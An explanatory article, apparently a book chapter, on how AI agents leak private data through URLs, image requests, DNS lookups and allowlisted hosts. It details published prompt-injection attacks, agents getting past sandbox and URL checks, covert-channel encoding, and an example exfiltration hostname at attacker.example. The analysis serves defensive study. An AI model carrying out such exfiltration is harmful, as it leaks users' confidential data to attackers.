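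The security company Imperva later worked out a simpler rule. According to Imperva's *From ChatBot To SpyBot*, the service searched the text that the user had supplied and approved any string it found there, even one that wasn't a web address. This text included custom instructions, which are standing preferences that ChatGPT applies to every chat. There were also exceptions for domains:

- a bare domain with no subdomain, path or query string always passed
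- any subdomain of `google.com` passed
- any address at all on `openai.com` passed

Rehberger's result doesn't fit this rule well, because all 36 of his addresses followed the same pattern and should have passed or failed together. OpenAI may have changed the check between the two tests, or the service may have treated text differently depending on its source. Both tests show that single-character addresses could get through.

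Imperva also found that the service approved any address that matched part of the user's text, even if the full address there was longer. An attacker could therefore plant one long address ending in the alphabet and get approval for shorter versions, each cut off at a different letter. The last letter of the version ChatGPT used revealed one letter of the stolen data. A third method used a separate domain for each character, at $1 or $2 per domain, and relied on the exception for bare domains.

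Imperva assumed that the attacker could already edit the victim's custom instructions to plant this text, for example through a flaw Imperva had found earlier in ChatGPT's website. That is a demanding condition, but the attack shows the weakness of trusting whatever the user supplied, because the service couldn't tell who had written it.

### The Azure bypass

The exceptions for domains turned out to be easier to exploit. In October 2024 Rehberger told OpenAI that `url_safe` approved addresses on `windows.net`, which includes Azure Blob Storage, and on `apache.org`. He could read request logs on both. Some of the bypasses still worked when he returned to the subject in 2025. Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* shows ChatGPT sending the user's recent chat history to Rehberger's storage account after reading a hostile document.

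Zenity Labs' *AgentFlayer* describes the same bypass in an attack on ChatGPT's connectors, which let ChatGPT search services such as Google Drive. A user uploads a document and asks ChatGPT to summarize it. Hidden text in the document makes ChatGPT search the user's Drive for API keys (passwords that programs use to log in to other services) and put them in an image address.

Zenity first used an address at Beeceptor, a service for testing web requests, and `url_safe` blocked it. Zenity then used an image in its own Azure storage and changed little else. The image appeared, and the Azure log contained the keys. Zenity couldn't see the check's code, but these results are good evidence of how it worked. Both addresses had secrets in the query string, so a true exact-URL check would have rejected both, but `url_safe` approved the one on a familiar domain.

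Rehberger recommended that OpenAI publish the list of safe domains and let business customers edit it. OpenAI instead tightened the check around August 2025, which stopped these attacks, according to Embrace The Red.

### OpenAI's index of public addresses

On 28 January 2026, OpenAI explained the design it now uses. A crawler, which is a program that visits public web pages, builds an index of the addresses it finds, much as a search engine does. The crawler has no access to users' conversations or accounts. Before ChatGPT automatically opens a page or displays an image, software looks for the exact address in this index. If the address is there, ChatGPT can load it. Otherwise, the software either has ChatGPT try another site or shows the user a warning and lets them decide.

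The address that leaked Ines's bid ended in `school-bid-4.18m-floor-3.95m`. It didn't exist until her assistant wrote it, so the crawler could not have recorded it.

One of OpenAI's two reasons for not using a list of trusted domains is that a trusted site may redirect to an untrusted one. This is a good argument against a check that covers only the first domain, such as `url_safe` when it approved Bing's tracking links. It is weaker against CSP, because the browser checks the host again after each redirect. Outsiders' logs and server-side fetches would have been stronger arguments, because CSP can't detect either.

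The other reason is that people visit many sites beyond the popular ones. A strict list would produce frequent warnings, and users would learn to click through them. OpenAI's design also has some of this problem. The index won't contain a page published a few minutes ago, a page behind a login, or a link that a company generated for one customer. If Ines's supplier emails her a link to track her delivery, the link is legitimate, but the software can't distinguish it from a leak because it is unique to her.

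The warning shows the address and says that the link is unverified and may contain information from the conversation. Ines might notice her price in the address if the attacker left the digits readable. If the attacker had the model encode them, she would see random-looking characters, like those in many tracking links.

OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (March 2026) calls the mechanism Safe Url and says it also covers pages and bookmarks opened in OpenAI's Atlas browser, and searches and page visits by its report-writing agent, Deep Research. Covering searches is sensible because a search query, like a URL, can contain private data.

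OpenAI promises only that the URL check prevents the agent from "quietly leaking user-specific data through the URL itself". The check doesn't make a page's contents trustworthy or stop a page from deceiving the user, and OpenAI treats it as one layer of defense alongside model training and monitoring.

Outside researchers can't easily measure how much the URL check contributes. In August 2026, Rahman and Kim found no leaks in 48 valid trials on ChatGPT, although the underlying model leaked in up to 100% of trials when they used it directly. They couldn't see which part of the product accounted for the difference, and it may not have been the URL check. Even if the trials were independent, no leaks in 48 would be compatible with a true leak rate of up to about 6%.

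The check also has to run wherever OpenAI's software loads an address. Rehberger's main practical worry was that some of OpenAI's own developers wouldn't know about the check. The Codex leak that PromptArmor reported in April 2026 suggests he was right to worry. Codex displayed an image whose address contained the text of the user's emails, and no public index could have included that address.

### Anthropic's rule for `web_fetch`

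Claude opens web pages with a tool called `web_fetch`. Anthropic made it available in September 2025 to developers using its API, the interface through which other companies' software uses Claude, and Willison (2025) singled out its approach to safety as particularly interesting. Claude may not compose an address. Anthropic's *Web fetch tool* states that Claude can fetch an address only if it has already appeared in one of these places:

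- a message from the user
- the result of a tool that the developer's own software runs
- the result of an earlier web search or page fetch

This rule needs no index. If a hostile page tells Claude to add the user's recent answers to an address and visit it, the software refuses because the resulting address has never appeared before. As Willison (2026) points out, these rules block the request deterministically, so rewording the instructions does not help the attacker.

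Claude could open Ines's tracking link if she pasted it into the chat. According to Embrace The Red, ChatGPT seems to make the same exception for links in the user's own messages. The exception is convenient, but it allows addresses that are neither public nor well known. If a developer's software pastes incoming emails into the user's message, every link in those emails is approved too, including an attacker's.

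Paul used the third source on the list, earlier page fetches, in the attack he published on 9 July 2026. He built a website for a fictional coffee shop that showed a special page to Claude and an ordinary one to everyone else. The special page claimed that AI assistants had to identify their users by following links to the right profile, one letter at a time. According to dyb's *The Read-Only Lie*, each page had 27 links, one for each letter and one for a hyphen. When Claude followed the link for "a", the server returned a page with 27 more links, each beginning with "a", and so on until the address contained the whole name.

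Claude visited only addresses that were on the page it had just fetched and never composed one itself, so the rule approved them all. The visits still revealed Paul's home city to the server. Paul had never told Claude where he lived, but Claude worked it out from the name of a hackathon he had attended at school.

Anthropic said it had already found the problem itself, and it didn't pay Paul a reward. It fixed the flaw by no longer letting `web_fetch` follow links found in pages it had fetched. As a result, Claude can no longer read a manual by clicking from one chapter to the next. As a compromise, dyb suggests letting Claude follow links only on domains that the user has named in the conversation.

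The fix doesn't seem to be on by default for developers. Anthropic's *網頁擷取工具*, a newer, Chinese-language version of the tool's documentation, still lists earlier fetches among the approved sources. A developer can exclude them with the `url_sources` setting.

The newer documentation also describes a less obvious loophole, which arises when a developer gives Claude a tool that runs code. Claude can write a program that prints an address containing private data. The address then appears in a tool result, so it is approved by default even though Claude wrote it. Developers can use `url_sources` to exclude that tool's results. They also need to consider tools that repeat Claude's text in error messages.

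`web_fetch` also refuses addresses that seem to contain a password or API key, unless the secret also appears in the user's own text or the developer's instructions. This would block a key copied whole into an address, but not one spelled out over several requests. Anthropic still advises against using the tool where Claude handles both sensitive data and untrusted text.

### Spelling a secret with approved addresses

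Paul's attack shows that a model can get a secret past an exact-URL check by choosing among approved URLs, none of which has to contain the secret. Computer scientists call this a covert channel, a way of communicating through something that wasn't designed for communication. dyb traces the idea to a 1973 paper by Butler Lampson. Tenable used another covert channel, an alphabet of Bing links, against ChatGPT, and researchers built two more against quite different checks.

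Legit Security's *CamoLeak* describes an attack on GitHub Copilot Chat, an assistant that answers questions about code on GitHub. The attacker proposes a change to a project and uses GitHub's invisible comment feature to hide instructions in the description. When another user asks Copilot about the proposal, Copilot follows the instructions with that user's permissions, so it can read the user's private code.

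GitHub's CSP blocked images from outside GitHub, and Copilot couldn't produce the signatures that GitHub's image proxy, Camo, requires. But GitHub signs image addresses for anyone who submits a document containing them. The researcher submitted one address for each letter and symbol, and put the signed versions into the hidden instructions. Copilot then displayed the private text as a row of invisible one-pixel images. Camo fetched each image from the researcher's server, so the researcher could read the text from the order of the requests.

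The researcher extracted the description of an unfixed security hole from a private project this way. He also had Copilot search the victim's code for the keys to an Amazon cloud account. By 14 August 2025, GitHub had fixed the flaw by turning off all images in Copilot Chat. The attack became public on 8 October, according to OECD's *GitHub Copilot Chat Vulnerability Exposes Private Code and Secrets* (2025).

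The signatures worked as GitHub designed them to. A signature proves that GitHub's software approved an address, and the attacker needed only ordinary, approved addresses.

Radware's *ZombieAgent* got around ChatGPT's checks in a similar way. After an earlier attack, OpenAI had stopped ChatGPT from adding data to the addresses it was given by preventing it from changing them. Radware's researcher sent the victim an email containing a fixed address for each letter and digit, plus one for spaces. When the user asked ChatGPT to do something with their Gmail, it read the email, found the private data and opened the address for each character in turn. The requests came from OpenAI's servers, so a policy in the user's browser would not have blocked them.

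Radware reported the flaw on 26 September 2025 and said three days later that an improved version of the attack worked every time. OpenAI fixed the flaw on 16 December, and Radware (2026) announced the attack on 8 January. According to *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, ChatGPT would now open a link from an email only if it was in a well-known public index or supplied by the user.

Approving exact URLs makes the attack harder, because an address that exists only in a hostile email no longer works. The attacker first has to publish a page for each letter and digit and wait for the crawler to find them. That isn't very difficult, since Rehberger notes that anyone with a fairly large blog probably already has 36 pages in the index and could assign a letter or digit to each. He adds that OpenAI acknowledges this remaining route in its paper on the design, *Preventing URL-Based Data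 Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*.

### How much can the choice reveal?

The size of this leak is measured in bits, where one bit is the answer to one yes-or-no question. A choice among N equally likely addresses carries log₂ N bits, which is how many times you have to halve N to reach one. A choice among 2 addresses carries 1 bit, a choice among 36 carries about 5.17, and a choice among 1,024 carries 10.

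Suppose the secret is a random password of 16 characters, each a lowercase letter or a digit. There are 36¹⁶ such passwords, or about 8 × 10²⁴, so the password contains 16 × 5.17 = 82.7 bits. If the attacker can see the order of the requests and the model can load an address more than once, the number of requests depends only on how many addresses the attacker has prepared:

- With 36 addresses, each request reveals one character, so the password takes 16 requests.
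- With 1,024 addresses, each request reveals 10 bits. Eight requests would reveal only 80 bits, so the password takes 9.

Preparing more addresses helps the attacker little, because doubling their number adds only one bit per request. To leak the whole password in one request, the attacker would need a separate address for every possible password, which means 8 × 10²⁴ pages, more than any crawler will ever index.

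For the same reason, OpenAI's index would have restricted Paul's attack more than it restricts one that uses an ordinary alphabet of pages. His server generated new pages as Claude browsed, but an independent crawler would have had to visit them beforehand. A ten-character name has 27¹⁰, or about 206 trillion, possible addresses. The crawler might index all 729 two-character pages, but it would never index all the ten-character ones.

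dyb estimates that Paul's attack took about 30 requests at 4.75 bits each, or 143 bits in total. That is the most such requests could carry. Names and cities are much more predictable than random characters, so what the server learned was worth fewer bits.

An exact-URL check is still a big improvement over a domain list. PromptArmor got the full text of several emails out of Superhuman in a single answer because the model could write any text after the host name. If an exact-URL check limits the attacker to one character per request, a 2,000-character email would take 2,000 requests. An attacker could prepare addresses for whole words to reduce that number, but the model would still have to make hundreds of requests without a mistake, and somebody might notice them.

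Short secrets can still leak. Suppose the attacker knows that the firm's bid is between 4 and 5 million and wants it to the nearest 10,000. There are only 100 possible answers, so the attacker prepares 100 addresses, one for each, and a single request reveals the bid. If the attacker only wants to know whether the firm is bidding at all, one address is enough, because the assistant can load it for yes and not load it for no.

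An exact-URL check would protect Ines's bid document, but it might not protect the most valuable number in it. OpenAI's Lockdown Mode goes further for people in her position because it limits the requests themselves.

### Would caching or a ban on repeat visits help?

Rehberger proposes two ways to reduce the remaining leak. The software could keep a copy of each page for a few minutes and reuse it if the model requested the page again, or it could refuse to load the same address twice in one session. Either way, the attacker's server would receive at most one request for each address during those minutes or that session.

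This would spoil the simplest version of the attack, because a password with two e's requires requesting the address for "e" twice, and the server would miss the second request. Only about 2% of random 16-character passwords have no repeated character.

But an attacker who knows that repeats are banned can use a different code. If the attacker can see the order of the requests, that order can encode the password. The first request can go to any of 36 addresses, the second to any of the remaining 35, and so on. With 17 requests there are about 3 × 10²⁴ possible sequences, fewer than the 8 × 10²⁴ possible passwords. With 18 there are about 6 × 10²⁵, enough to give every password its own sequence. The ban on repeats therefore raises the minimum from 16 requests to 18. The model would have to convert the password into the right sequence, which is easy if it can run code but awkward otherwise.

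Losing the order hurts the attacker much more. Browsers often load several images at once, and the requests may arrive in any order. If each of the 36 addresses can appear only once and the order means nothing, the server learns only whether each one was loaded. That is 36 yes-or-no answers, so at most 36 bits, which is enough for six characters of the password. (dyb points out that the timing of requests can also carry information, and this figure ignores it.)

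Radware's attack gets around this too. To keep the characters in order, the researcher prepared a separate address for each character in each position, so "a" in the first position had a different address from "a" in the second. A 16-character password with 36 possible characters in each position takes 16 × 36 = 576 addresses. The model loads 16 of them, never uses one twice, and can load them in any order.

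| Addresses prepared | Can an address load twice? | Can the attacker see the order? | Requests needed for the password |
|---|---|---|---|
| 36 | Yes | Yes | 16 |
| 1,024 | Yes | Yes | 9 |
| 36 | No | Yes | 18 |
| 36 | No | No | Impossible, at most 36 bits get out |
| 576, one per character and position | No | No | 16 |

Rehberger's proposals would therefore force an attacker to prepare more addresses, but would not stop the leak. Paul's attack would have needed no changes, because each address was one character longer than the last, so none repeated.

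In CamoLeak, the researcher got past the cache another way, by having Copilot add a fresh random number to the end of each signed address so that every request looked new. Camo evidently accepted the altered addresses, so it must not have been checking the whole address. A check that compared every character would have rejected them.

The ban also lasts only one session. Radware got ChatGPT to save hostile instructions in its memory, so that it leaked a little more each time the user came back. An attacker who does this can reuse the same 36 addresses in every new session.

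Limiting the number of requests is probably more effective. Rehberger suggested in 2023 that ChatGPT should display only a handful of images per answer. Five requests, each to one of 1,024 addresses, can carry at most 50 bits, or nine characters of the password, if the attacker learns only which addresses were loaded and in what order. Anthropic's `web_fetch` has a setting for this, `max_uses`, but there is no limit unless the developer sets one. A strict limit hinders research tasks, in which an agent may need to open 50 pages.

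If developers don't restrict which links an agent can follow, dyb suggests that they at least watch for suspicious patterns, such as a quick series of requests to one site in which each address is one character longer than the last. This would have caught Paul's attack early but missed ZombieAgent, whose addresses were all about the same length. Attackers can also change the pattern of their requests more easily than they can get around a restriction on links.

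A cache could protect much better if OpenAI's crawler filled it instead of the model's requests. The crawler already visits web pages to build the index. If it also saved them, ChatGPT could read the saved copies without sending a request to the attacker's server. The attacker could then learn nothing from which page ChatGPT opened, however many addresses were in the index. An ordinary cache doesn't achieve this because the first request for each page still goes to the site, and the attacker can make sure that every request is a first request. However, saved copies go out of date. They would be adequate for a building regulation or a product manual, but not for the weather on the day of Ines's site visit.

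## Do domain allowlists work for agents that make their own network requests?

Suppose Ines's firm gives her an agent that can write and run programs, and she asks it to build a cost model from the bid documents and a supplier's price list. The agent writes a program, downloads a charting library and runs everything in a sandbox, an isolated computing environment with its own files. Text hidden in the price list tells the agent to send the bid documents to the attacker.

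An agent that makes its own network requests can leak much more than an assistant that only displays text. An image address usually holds a few thousand characters at most, but a program run by the agent can put a whole file in the body of a request, the part that carries uploads. The program can also include credentials, such as an API key, which determine whose account receives the file. It opens its own connections, so no browser checks its requests against a CSP. The agent's ordinary work may also require access to sites like GitHub, where anyone can store data.

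OpenAI's *Agent internet access*, part of the documentation for its programming agent Codex, gives an example in which a user asks Codex to fix a problem described in a GitHub issue, a public report that anyone can write. The issue includes a command that supposedly reproduces the problem but, if Codex runs it, sends the message attached to the project's latest saved change to an outside server.

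### How an egress proxy works

The equivalent of the browser's check is an egress proxy, a gateway through which a sandbox's outbound traffic must pass. Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent, can use one for the commands it runs on a user's computer, and Anthropic documents it in detail. Suppose Ines's agent had the same design and its allowlist contained only `packages.example`, the source of its libraries:

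1. The operating system gives the program no route to the internet except through the proxy, which runs outside the sandbox.
2. The program asks the proxy to connect it to a host.
3. The proxy compares the host name with the list. If it finds no match, it refuses the connection or waits for someone to approve it.
4. If the name matches, the proxy looks up the host's numeric address, connects to it and passes data in both directions.

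In Claude Code's sandbox, the operating system blocks any connection that bypasses the proxy, regardless of what the model decides to run. This block is essential because programs learn about the proxy from settings that they can ignore. It also stops some harmless tools, including most database programs, which open their own connections instead of using the proxy and so fail even when their host is on the allowlist.

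As with a CSP, a redirect from `packages.example` to an unlisted host fails, because the program has to request a second connection through the proxy. But if the `packages.example` server fetches a URL itself, that request doesn't pass through the proxy.

In its fourth step, Anthropic's proxy also refuses a domain name that resolves only to local addresses, such as those of the user's machine. Otherwise, an attacker who controlled an allowed domain name could point it to a private service at one of those addresses.

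The comparison in the third step has to be exact. ThaiCERT's *Anthropic Patches Claude Code Vulnerability That Could Bypass Sandbox Restrictions* describes a flaw that affected wildcard entries from October 2025 until Anthropic fixed it in March 2026. An attacker could write a host name with their own host first, then a null byte (an invisible character that some software treats as the end of a text), then an allowed domain. The check accepted the name because of its ending, but the proxy read only the part before the null byte and connected to the attacker's host. The EchoLeak attack on Copilot exploited a similar mismatch between a filter and the software that displayed its output.

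### What encryption hides from the proxy

Most web traffic uses HTTPS, which encrypts a request before it leaves the program. The program tells the proxy which host it wants, but everything after that passes through as encrypted data. By default, Anthropic's proxy doesn't decrypt it, so it can't distinguish a library download from an upload of the bid documents to the same host. It sees even less than the browser does when it enforces a CSP:

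| Part of an HTTPS request | CSP in the browser | Proxy that doesn't decrypt | Proxy that decrypts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Host and port | Checks | Checks | Can check |
| Path | Usually checks | Can't see | Can check |
| Query string | Ignores | Can't see | Can check |
| Credentials | Ignores | Can't see | Can check |
| Body | Ignores | Can't see | Can check |

A program can also misstate its destination, a technique known as domain fronting. An HTTPS request sent through a proxy names its destination once to the proxy and again inside the encryption. Because content delivery networks serve many customers' websites from the same machines, a program can name an allowed site to the proxy and an attacker's site on the same network inside the encryption. If the network accepts the mismatch, it delivers the request to the attacker. Docker, which also makes sandboxes for agents, calls this inherent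 to HTTPS proxying, but a proxy that decrypts traffic can compare the two names.

To decrypt traffic, the proxy impersonates the destination server, using a certificate that the sandbox is configured to trust. It checks the request, then encrypts it again for the real server. Anthropic recommends a custom proxy of this kind for users who need stronger guarantees. However, the proxy can read every password that passes through it, and some programs reject its certificate.

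Decryption also lets the proxy keep credentials out of the sandbox. Claude Code has an experimental setting that gives programs a placeholder instead of a real API key. The proxy replaces the placeholder with the key only in requests to hosts the user has chosen. A hostile program can still misuse the key by sending requests to those hosts, but it can't steal the key. This setting doesn't make the proxy inspect the rest of the request for private data.

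### Leaks through name lookups

A sandbox that blocks every forbidden connection can still leak data through DNS lookups, as browsers did when they prefetched host names. If the program is allowed to look up names itself, it can look up `school-bid-4-18m.attacker.example`, which sends that name, and the data in it, to the attacker's DNS server. The proxy doesn't prevent this because the program doesn't need to connect to that host.

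Zenity Labs' *It's Always DNS in Claude’s Sandbox* found this problem in the environment where Anthropic's assistant Claude runs code. The researcher put a document in Google Drive that looked like a company AI policy and told Claude to carry out a mandatory test of the sandbox's security. When the user asked for a summary of the document, Claude saved an earlier chat message to a file and tried to contact a host whose name included the file's contents. The proxy refused the connection, but the DNS lookup had already carried the message out of the sandbox.

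At first, Claude kept removing the message from the host name, so the researcher had the command insert the file's contents as it ran. That way, Claude never wrote out the full name. This is a reason not to rely on the model to detect a leak.

Zenity Labs reported the flaw on 28 November 2025 and confirmed on 12 December that it could no longer get data out. By 29 May 2026, the same test got data out again. Anthropic already knew about the problem from another researcher. A newer deployment had undone the fix. An automatic test after each update could have caught this. A program in the sandbox would look up a unique name, and the test would check whether the query reached an outside DNS server.

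The second time, Zenity Labs also used the DNS replies, which can carry text. The researcher's server sent commands in its replies, and a program in the sandbox sent back the results in new lookups. This gave the researcher remote control of the sandbox until the program ended.

Two other companies had the same gap. Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026) describes it in the environment where ChatGPT runs code. In one test, a custom GPT posing as a doctor assessed a patient's laboratory results. The researchers' server received the patient's name and the assessment, although ChatGPT told the user that it had not sent the data anywhere. OpenAI had already found the underlying problem and finished deploying a fix on 20 February 2026.

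The other case involved AgentCore, a service that Amazon Web Services (AWS) rents to companies that build agents. AWS had advertised its sandbox mode as having no external access, but the sandbox allowed DNS queries. BeyondTrust's *AWS Bedrock AgentCore Code Interpreter’s ‘Sandbox’ mode allows DNS queries* (2026) records a long dispute over this flaw. The security company reported it in September 2025. AWS deployed a fix in November, withdrew it, and decided in December to change the documentation instead. It said the sandbox needed DNS to reach Amazon's storage service. BeyondTrust published its findings on 16 March 2026, and AWS closed the leak a month later.

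Sending data through DNS is slower than an ordinary upload but fast enough for documents. BeyondTrust put up to 60 characters of encoded data in each lookup. Every four characters encoded three bytes, so each lookup carried up to 45 bytes. At that rate, the firm's price would fit in one lookup, and a 2,000-character email in plain English would take 45.

The fix is to give the sandbox no DNS server of its own. In the local version of Claude Code's sandbox on Linux, a program has no network to send DNS lookups over, so it passes the host name to the proxy, which looks it up only after checking that it is on the allowlist. If a program must do its own lookups, as AWS wanted, the sandbox's DNS server can resolve listed names and block queries for any others without forwarding them.

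### What coding agents allow by default

Most users probably keep the network settings that they are given, so the defaults matter more than the options. OpenAI, Anthropic and GitHub have made quite different choices:

| Agent | Default access for the commands it runs | Listed domains | What the list doesn't cover |
|---|---|---|---|
| OpenAI Codex in the cloud | None | None, with an optional preset of 71 | Setup scripts |
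| Claude Code on the user's computer | No network limit, because the sandbox is off | None at first, once the user turns the sandbox on | Claude's own web tools, MCP servers and some helper programs |
| Claude Code in the cloud | Limited to a list | More than 100 | GitHub traffic and MCP connectors |
| GitHub's Copilot cloud agent | Limited to a list | GitHub's own hosts, plus common sources of software | MCP servers and setup steps |

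OpenAI's default is the strictest. According to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*, setup scripts first download whatever the project needs, and then the agent works offline. Willison called this approach sensible when OpenAI introduced optional internet access in June 2025. A user who turns access on can start from an empty list, allow everything, or choose a preset called "common dependencies", which lists 71 domains that programmers often download from. OpenAI's current documentation has the same defaults and the same 71 entries.

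Some of these entries would fail the test that no outsider can host, log or store anything on an allowlisted domain. The list includes `github.com`, where anyone can open an account and upload files, and `apache.org`, where Rehberger could read request logs in 2024. If the entry for `google.com` covers subdomains, it also allows Google Forms and Apps Script, which carried data out of Superhuman and Bard. The agent no longer needs the entry for `rubyforge.org`, which hosted software projects until it closed in 2014, though that domain's registration hasn't necessarily lapsed, as the Agentforce domain's had.

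Claude Code's local sandbox starts with an empty allowlist and prompts the user about each new host. But the user has to turn the sandbox on, and if it can't start, Claude Code by default runs commands without it. The sandbox also doesn't work on Windows unless the user runs Claude Code inside a Linux environment. Administrators can change these defaults for a whole company, for example by preventing Claude Code from starting without a working sandbox.

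When the sandbox blocks a command, Claude can also request to run it again outside the sandbox. In Claude Code's automatic mode, Claude lists the extra hosts that a command needs, and a second model decides whether to allow them for that command. This saves the user from constant questions, but an attacker who gets Claude to request a host then only has to get the second model to approve it. With the `strictAllowlist` setting, Claude Code refuses any host that isn't already on the list. A separate setting disables the retry outside the sandbox.

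In the cloud, Anthropic starts with a much longer list. It includes `*.amazonaws.com`, which also appeared in Agentforce's policy, Google's storage service, and an address where the monitoring company Datadog receives its customers' logs. Outsiders can open accounts with all three companies. Anthropic gives much narrower access to GitHub than allowing `github.com` would. A separate proxy holds the user's GitHub credentials and answers requests to GitHub's API only for projects attached to the session.

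GitHub turns on its firewall and a recommended allowlist by default. The allowlist covers sites that distribute programming libraries, operating system packages and containers (programs bundled with everything they need to run). When the firewall blocks a request, Copilot adds a warning to its proposed code change with the blocked address and the command that tried to reach it. Reviewers can then spot an attempted leak or a site missing from the allowlist without searching through logs.

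GitHub also lets customers limit an allowlist entry to a path, such as one project's folder on a package server, but for HTTPS traffic this works only if the firewall can decrypt the requests. The firewall controls only processes that the agent starts through its command-line tool, and GitHub warns that sophisticated attacks may get around it.

All four designs leave some network route that the allowlist doesn't cover. Setup scripts are less risky because they run before the agent reads anything, although a malicious library could still misuse the connection. MCP servers are a greater concern because the agent uses them while it works, often with access to a company's private data. Anyone comparing these products needs to check each route separately, since a product with a short domain list can also have a connector that sends data anywhere.

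### Does it help to allow only GET requests?

Codex users can also restrict requests to the GET, HEAD and OPTIONS methods. This blocks POST and PUT, the usual methods for uploads. The command in OpenAI's example uses POST, so it would fail even if its destination were on the allowlist.

The restriction makes `github.com` much safer to allow. Git, the usual tool for sending code to GitHub, uploads changes with POST, so a hostile program could no longer push the firm's bid to an attacker's project. The agent could still install most libraries, because they are downloaded with GET. But it could not copy a project with Git, which also uses POST to request the changes it downloads.

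A GET request can still carry data out in its path or query string, as an image request does. The attacker needs an allowlisted host where outsiders can read incoming requests or where a GET request stores data. Google Forms stores data this way, as Willison pointed out in the Superhuman case. Software can split a larger document across hundreds of requests, each holding a few thousand characters, and send them without making a mistake. In the alphabet attacks on chat assistants, by contrast, the model had to choose each address itself.

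Data may leak slowly even through sites that only distribute software. The main package registries for JavaScript and Python publish download statistics. An attacker could upload one obscure package for each letter and see which download counts rise after the agent has downloaded some of them. Automatic downloads by other services would make the results unreliable, and the statistics don't show the order of the letters, but the method could still reveal the answer to a yes-or-no question.

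The proxy has to decrypt HTTPS traffic to enforce the restriction on HTTP methods, because the method is encrypted. OpenAI's *Cloud environments* states that all outbound traffic from Codex's cloud environments passes through a proxy. A company that builds its own sandbox and copies only the domain list would not get the protection of the method restriction.

### Google Antigravity: a request logger on the default list

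Google's programming assistant Antigravity has an allowlist for its browser tool, which lets the Gemini model open websites and test the applications it is building. Google's *Allowlist / Denylist* explains that the browser asks the user before it opens an unlisted site. When users install Antigravity, they can fill the list with a default set of sites, which included `webhook.site`, a service that records the requests sent to it.

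PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data*, covered by Willison (2025), describes an attack on a programmer who asks Gemini for help connecting an application to Oracle's accounting software and supplies a guide found online. The guide contains instructions in one-point type for Gemini to collect code and passwords, add them to a `webhook.site` address and open that address in the browser. Gemini follows the instructions without the browser asking for permission, and the attacker reads the passwords in the site's log.

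Antigravity's default settings also blocked Gemini's file-reading tool from opening the file that contained the passwords. Gemini got around this by printing the file with a terminal command, which the restriction didn't cover. Domain lists can fail for the same reason if they apply to one tool and the agent has another that can do the same job.

Removing `webhook.site` from the allowlist would have made the browser ask the user about this address. That would have been an improvement, but PromptArmor found three more leaks that didn't use the browser tool. Antigravity also encourages people to run several agents in the background, and someone who returns to a queue of requests may approve them without much thought. PromptArmor published the flaw without first reporting it to Google, because Google already warned users about data theft when they opened the program.

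### Claude Cowork: an allowed host and the attacker's account

Anthropic's Cowork is an agent for office tasks that works with files on the user's computer. It runs code in a virtual machine, a simulated computer with its own operating system, and a proxy lets the machine connect only to a list of approved domains. The list includes `api.anthropic.com`, the address of Anthropic's programming interface. On 14 January, shortly after Cowork's release, Willison (2026) relayed an attack that used this address.

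In PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files*, a user connects a folder of confidential property documents and uploads a file of instructions found online. The file contains hidden text and an API key for the attacker's Anthropic account. Claude follows the hidden text and uses the key to upload a loan document to Anthropic's file storage. Cowork doesn't ask for approval, and the attacker can then open the document or ask Claude questions about it. PromptArmor demonstrated this with the smaller model Haiku, and got the stronger Opus 4.5 to leak customer records the same way.

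An exact-URL check would not have helped either, because every part of the web address was legitimate. All of Anthropic's customers upload files to the same address, and the API key determines where each file goes. The address contains nearly everything an attacker can control in an image request, but in an upload the key and the body matter more.

Rehberger had already found this route in Claude's chat product, as Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* describes. He noticed that Anthropic's own domain was the first entry on a list supposedly limited to sources of software packages. Anthropic acknowledged his report but had not closed the route when it released Cowork.

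Anthropic later added a second proxy inside the virtual machine. According to InfoQ (2026), it accepts only the session token that Anthropic issued to that machine, so it blocks requests that use an attacker's key. The proxy also blocks request headers that would make Anthropic's servers fetch something from another address. Forkast reports that Anthropic concluded that an attacker could try to misuse any function reachable through a listed domain.

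This fix is stronger than removing the upload command or training Claude to refuse, because the attacker can't obtain a valid token by rewriting the hostile text. However, the fix was easy for Anthropic only because Anthropic runs both the sandbox and the destination. To protect an entry like `*.amazonaws.com` similarly, a company's proxy would have to recognise which Amazon customer owns the account behind each request. It would be easier for the company to replace the wildcard with the exact hosts of its own storage.

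### Atlassian Rovo: a web tool that stayed on

Atlassian's AI agent, Rovo, can read the tasks companies track in Jira and the internal documents they keep in Confluence. In August 2026, PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls* showed that a hostile document could make Rovo add data from these tasks and documents to an attacker's web address and open it. Rovo's tool for opening web pages didn't check whether Rovo had written the address itself. Anthropic's rule for `web_fetch` would have blocked that address.

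Administrators could turn off Rovo's web search for their whole organisation, but the attack still worked because the setting removed the tool that searched for pages and left the one that opened them. An administrator who saw that web search was off could reasonably have concluded that Rovo had no internet access. A single proxy around all of Rovo's tools would have let the setting cut off that access, as people expected.

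PromptArmor had reported the flaw on 23 May. Atlassian thanked the researchers but sent nothing further in more than two months, and the attack still worked when PromptArmor published its findings.

On 7 August, Varonis published a separate flaw it had found and named RovoBlast. *Researchers Uncover RovoBlast Vulnerability in Atlassian AI Assistant* (Mascellino, 2026) reports that an attacker could put instructions for Rovo in a link. After one click, Rovo collected company data and sent it out through its research agent, which can browse any website. Atlassian has fixed this flaw. A strict domain allowlist would have blocked the last step, but it would also have stopped the agent from researching the open web, which is its purpose. Controlling which addresses such an agent can write, or keeping private data away from it, makes more sense.

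### GitHub: a leak in a public pull request

An agent can also leak data through an action that its user has authorised. In May 2025 the security company Invariant Labs demonstrated this with GitHub's MCP server, which lets an agent read and change projects using the user's GitHub account. The user in the demonstration had one public project and several private ones.

The attacker wrote an issue in the public project, as any GitHub user can. When the user asked the agent to look at the project's open issues, the attacker's text led it to read the private projects too. The agent then put what it had found in a pull request, which is a proposed change to a project. The pull request was public because the project was, and it revealed the names of private projects and personal details, including the user's salary.

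No list of destinations would have flagged this, because the agent contacted only GitHub, which it needed for the task, and the pull request went to the user's own project. The account check that fixed Cowork would not have helped either, because the agent used the right account. Even if a proxy had decrypted the request, it would have found nothing unusual about the pull request unless it could detect that some of the text came from a private project.

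Limiting what the agent could read would have helped. If the user had run the task in Claude Code's cloud service with only the public project attached, Anthropic's GitHub proxy would have refused requests for the private ones. This protection isn't available when a task needs both, such as copying a fix from a private project to a public one. The software then has to separate text that may be made public from text that must stay private.

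### What carries over from web pages?

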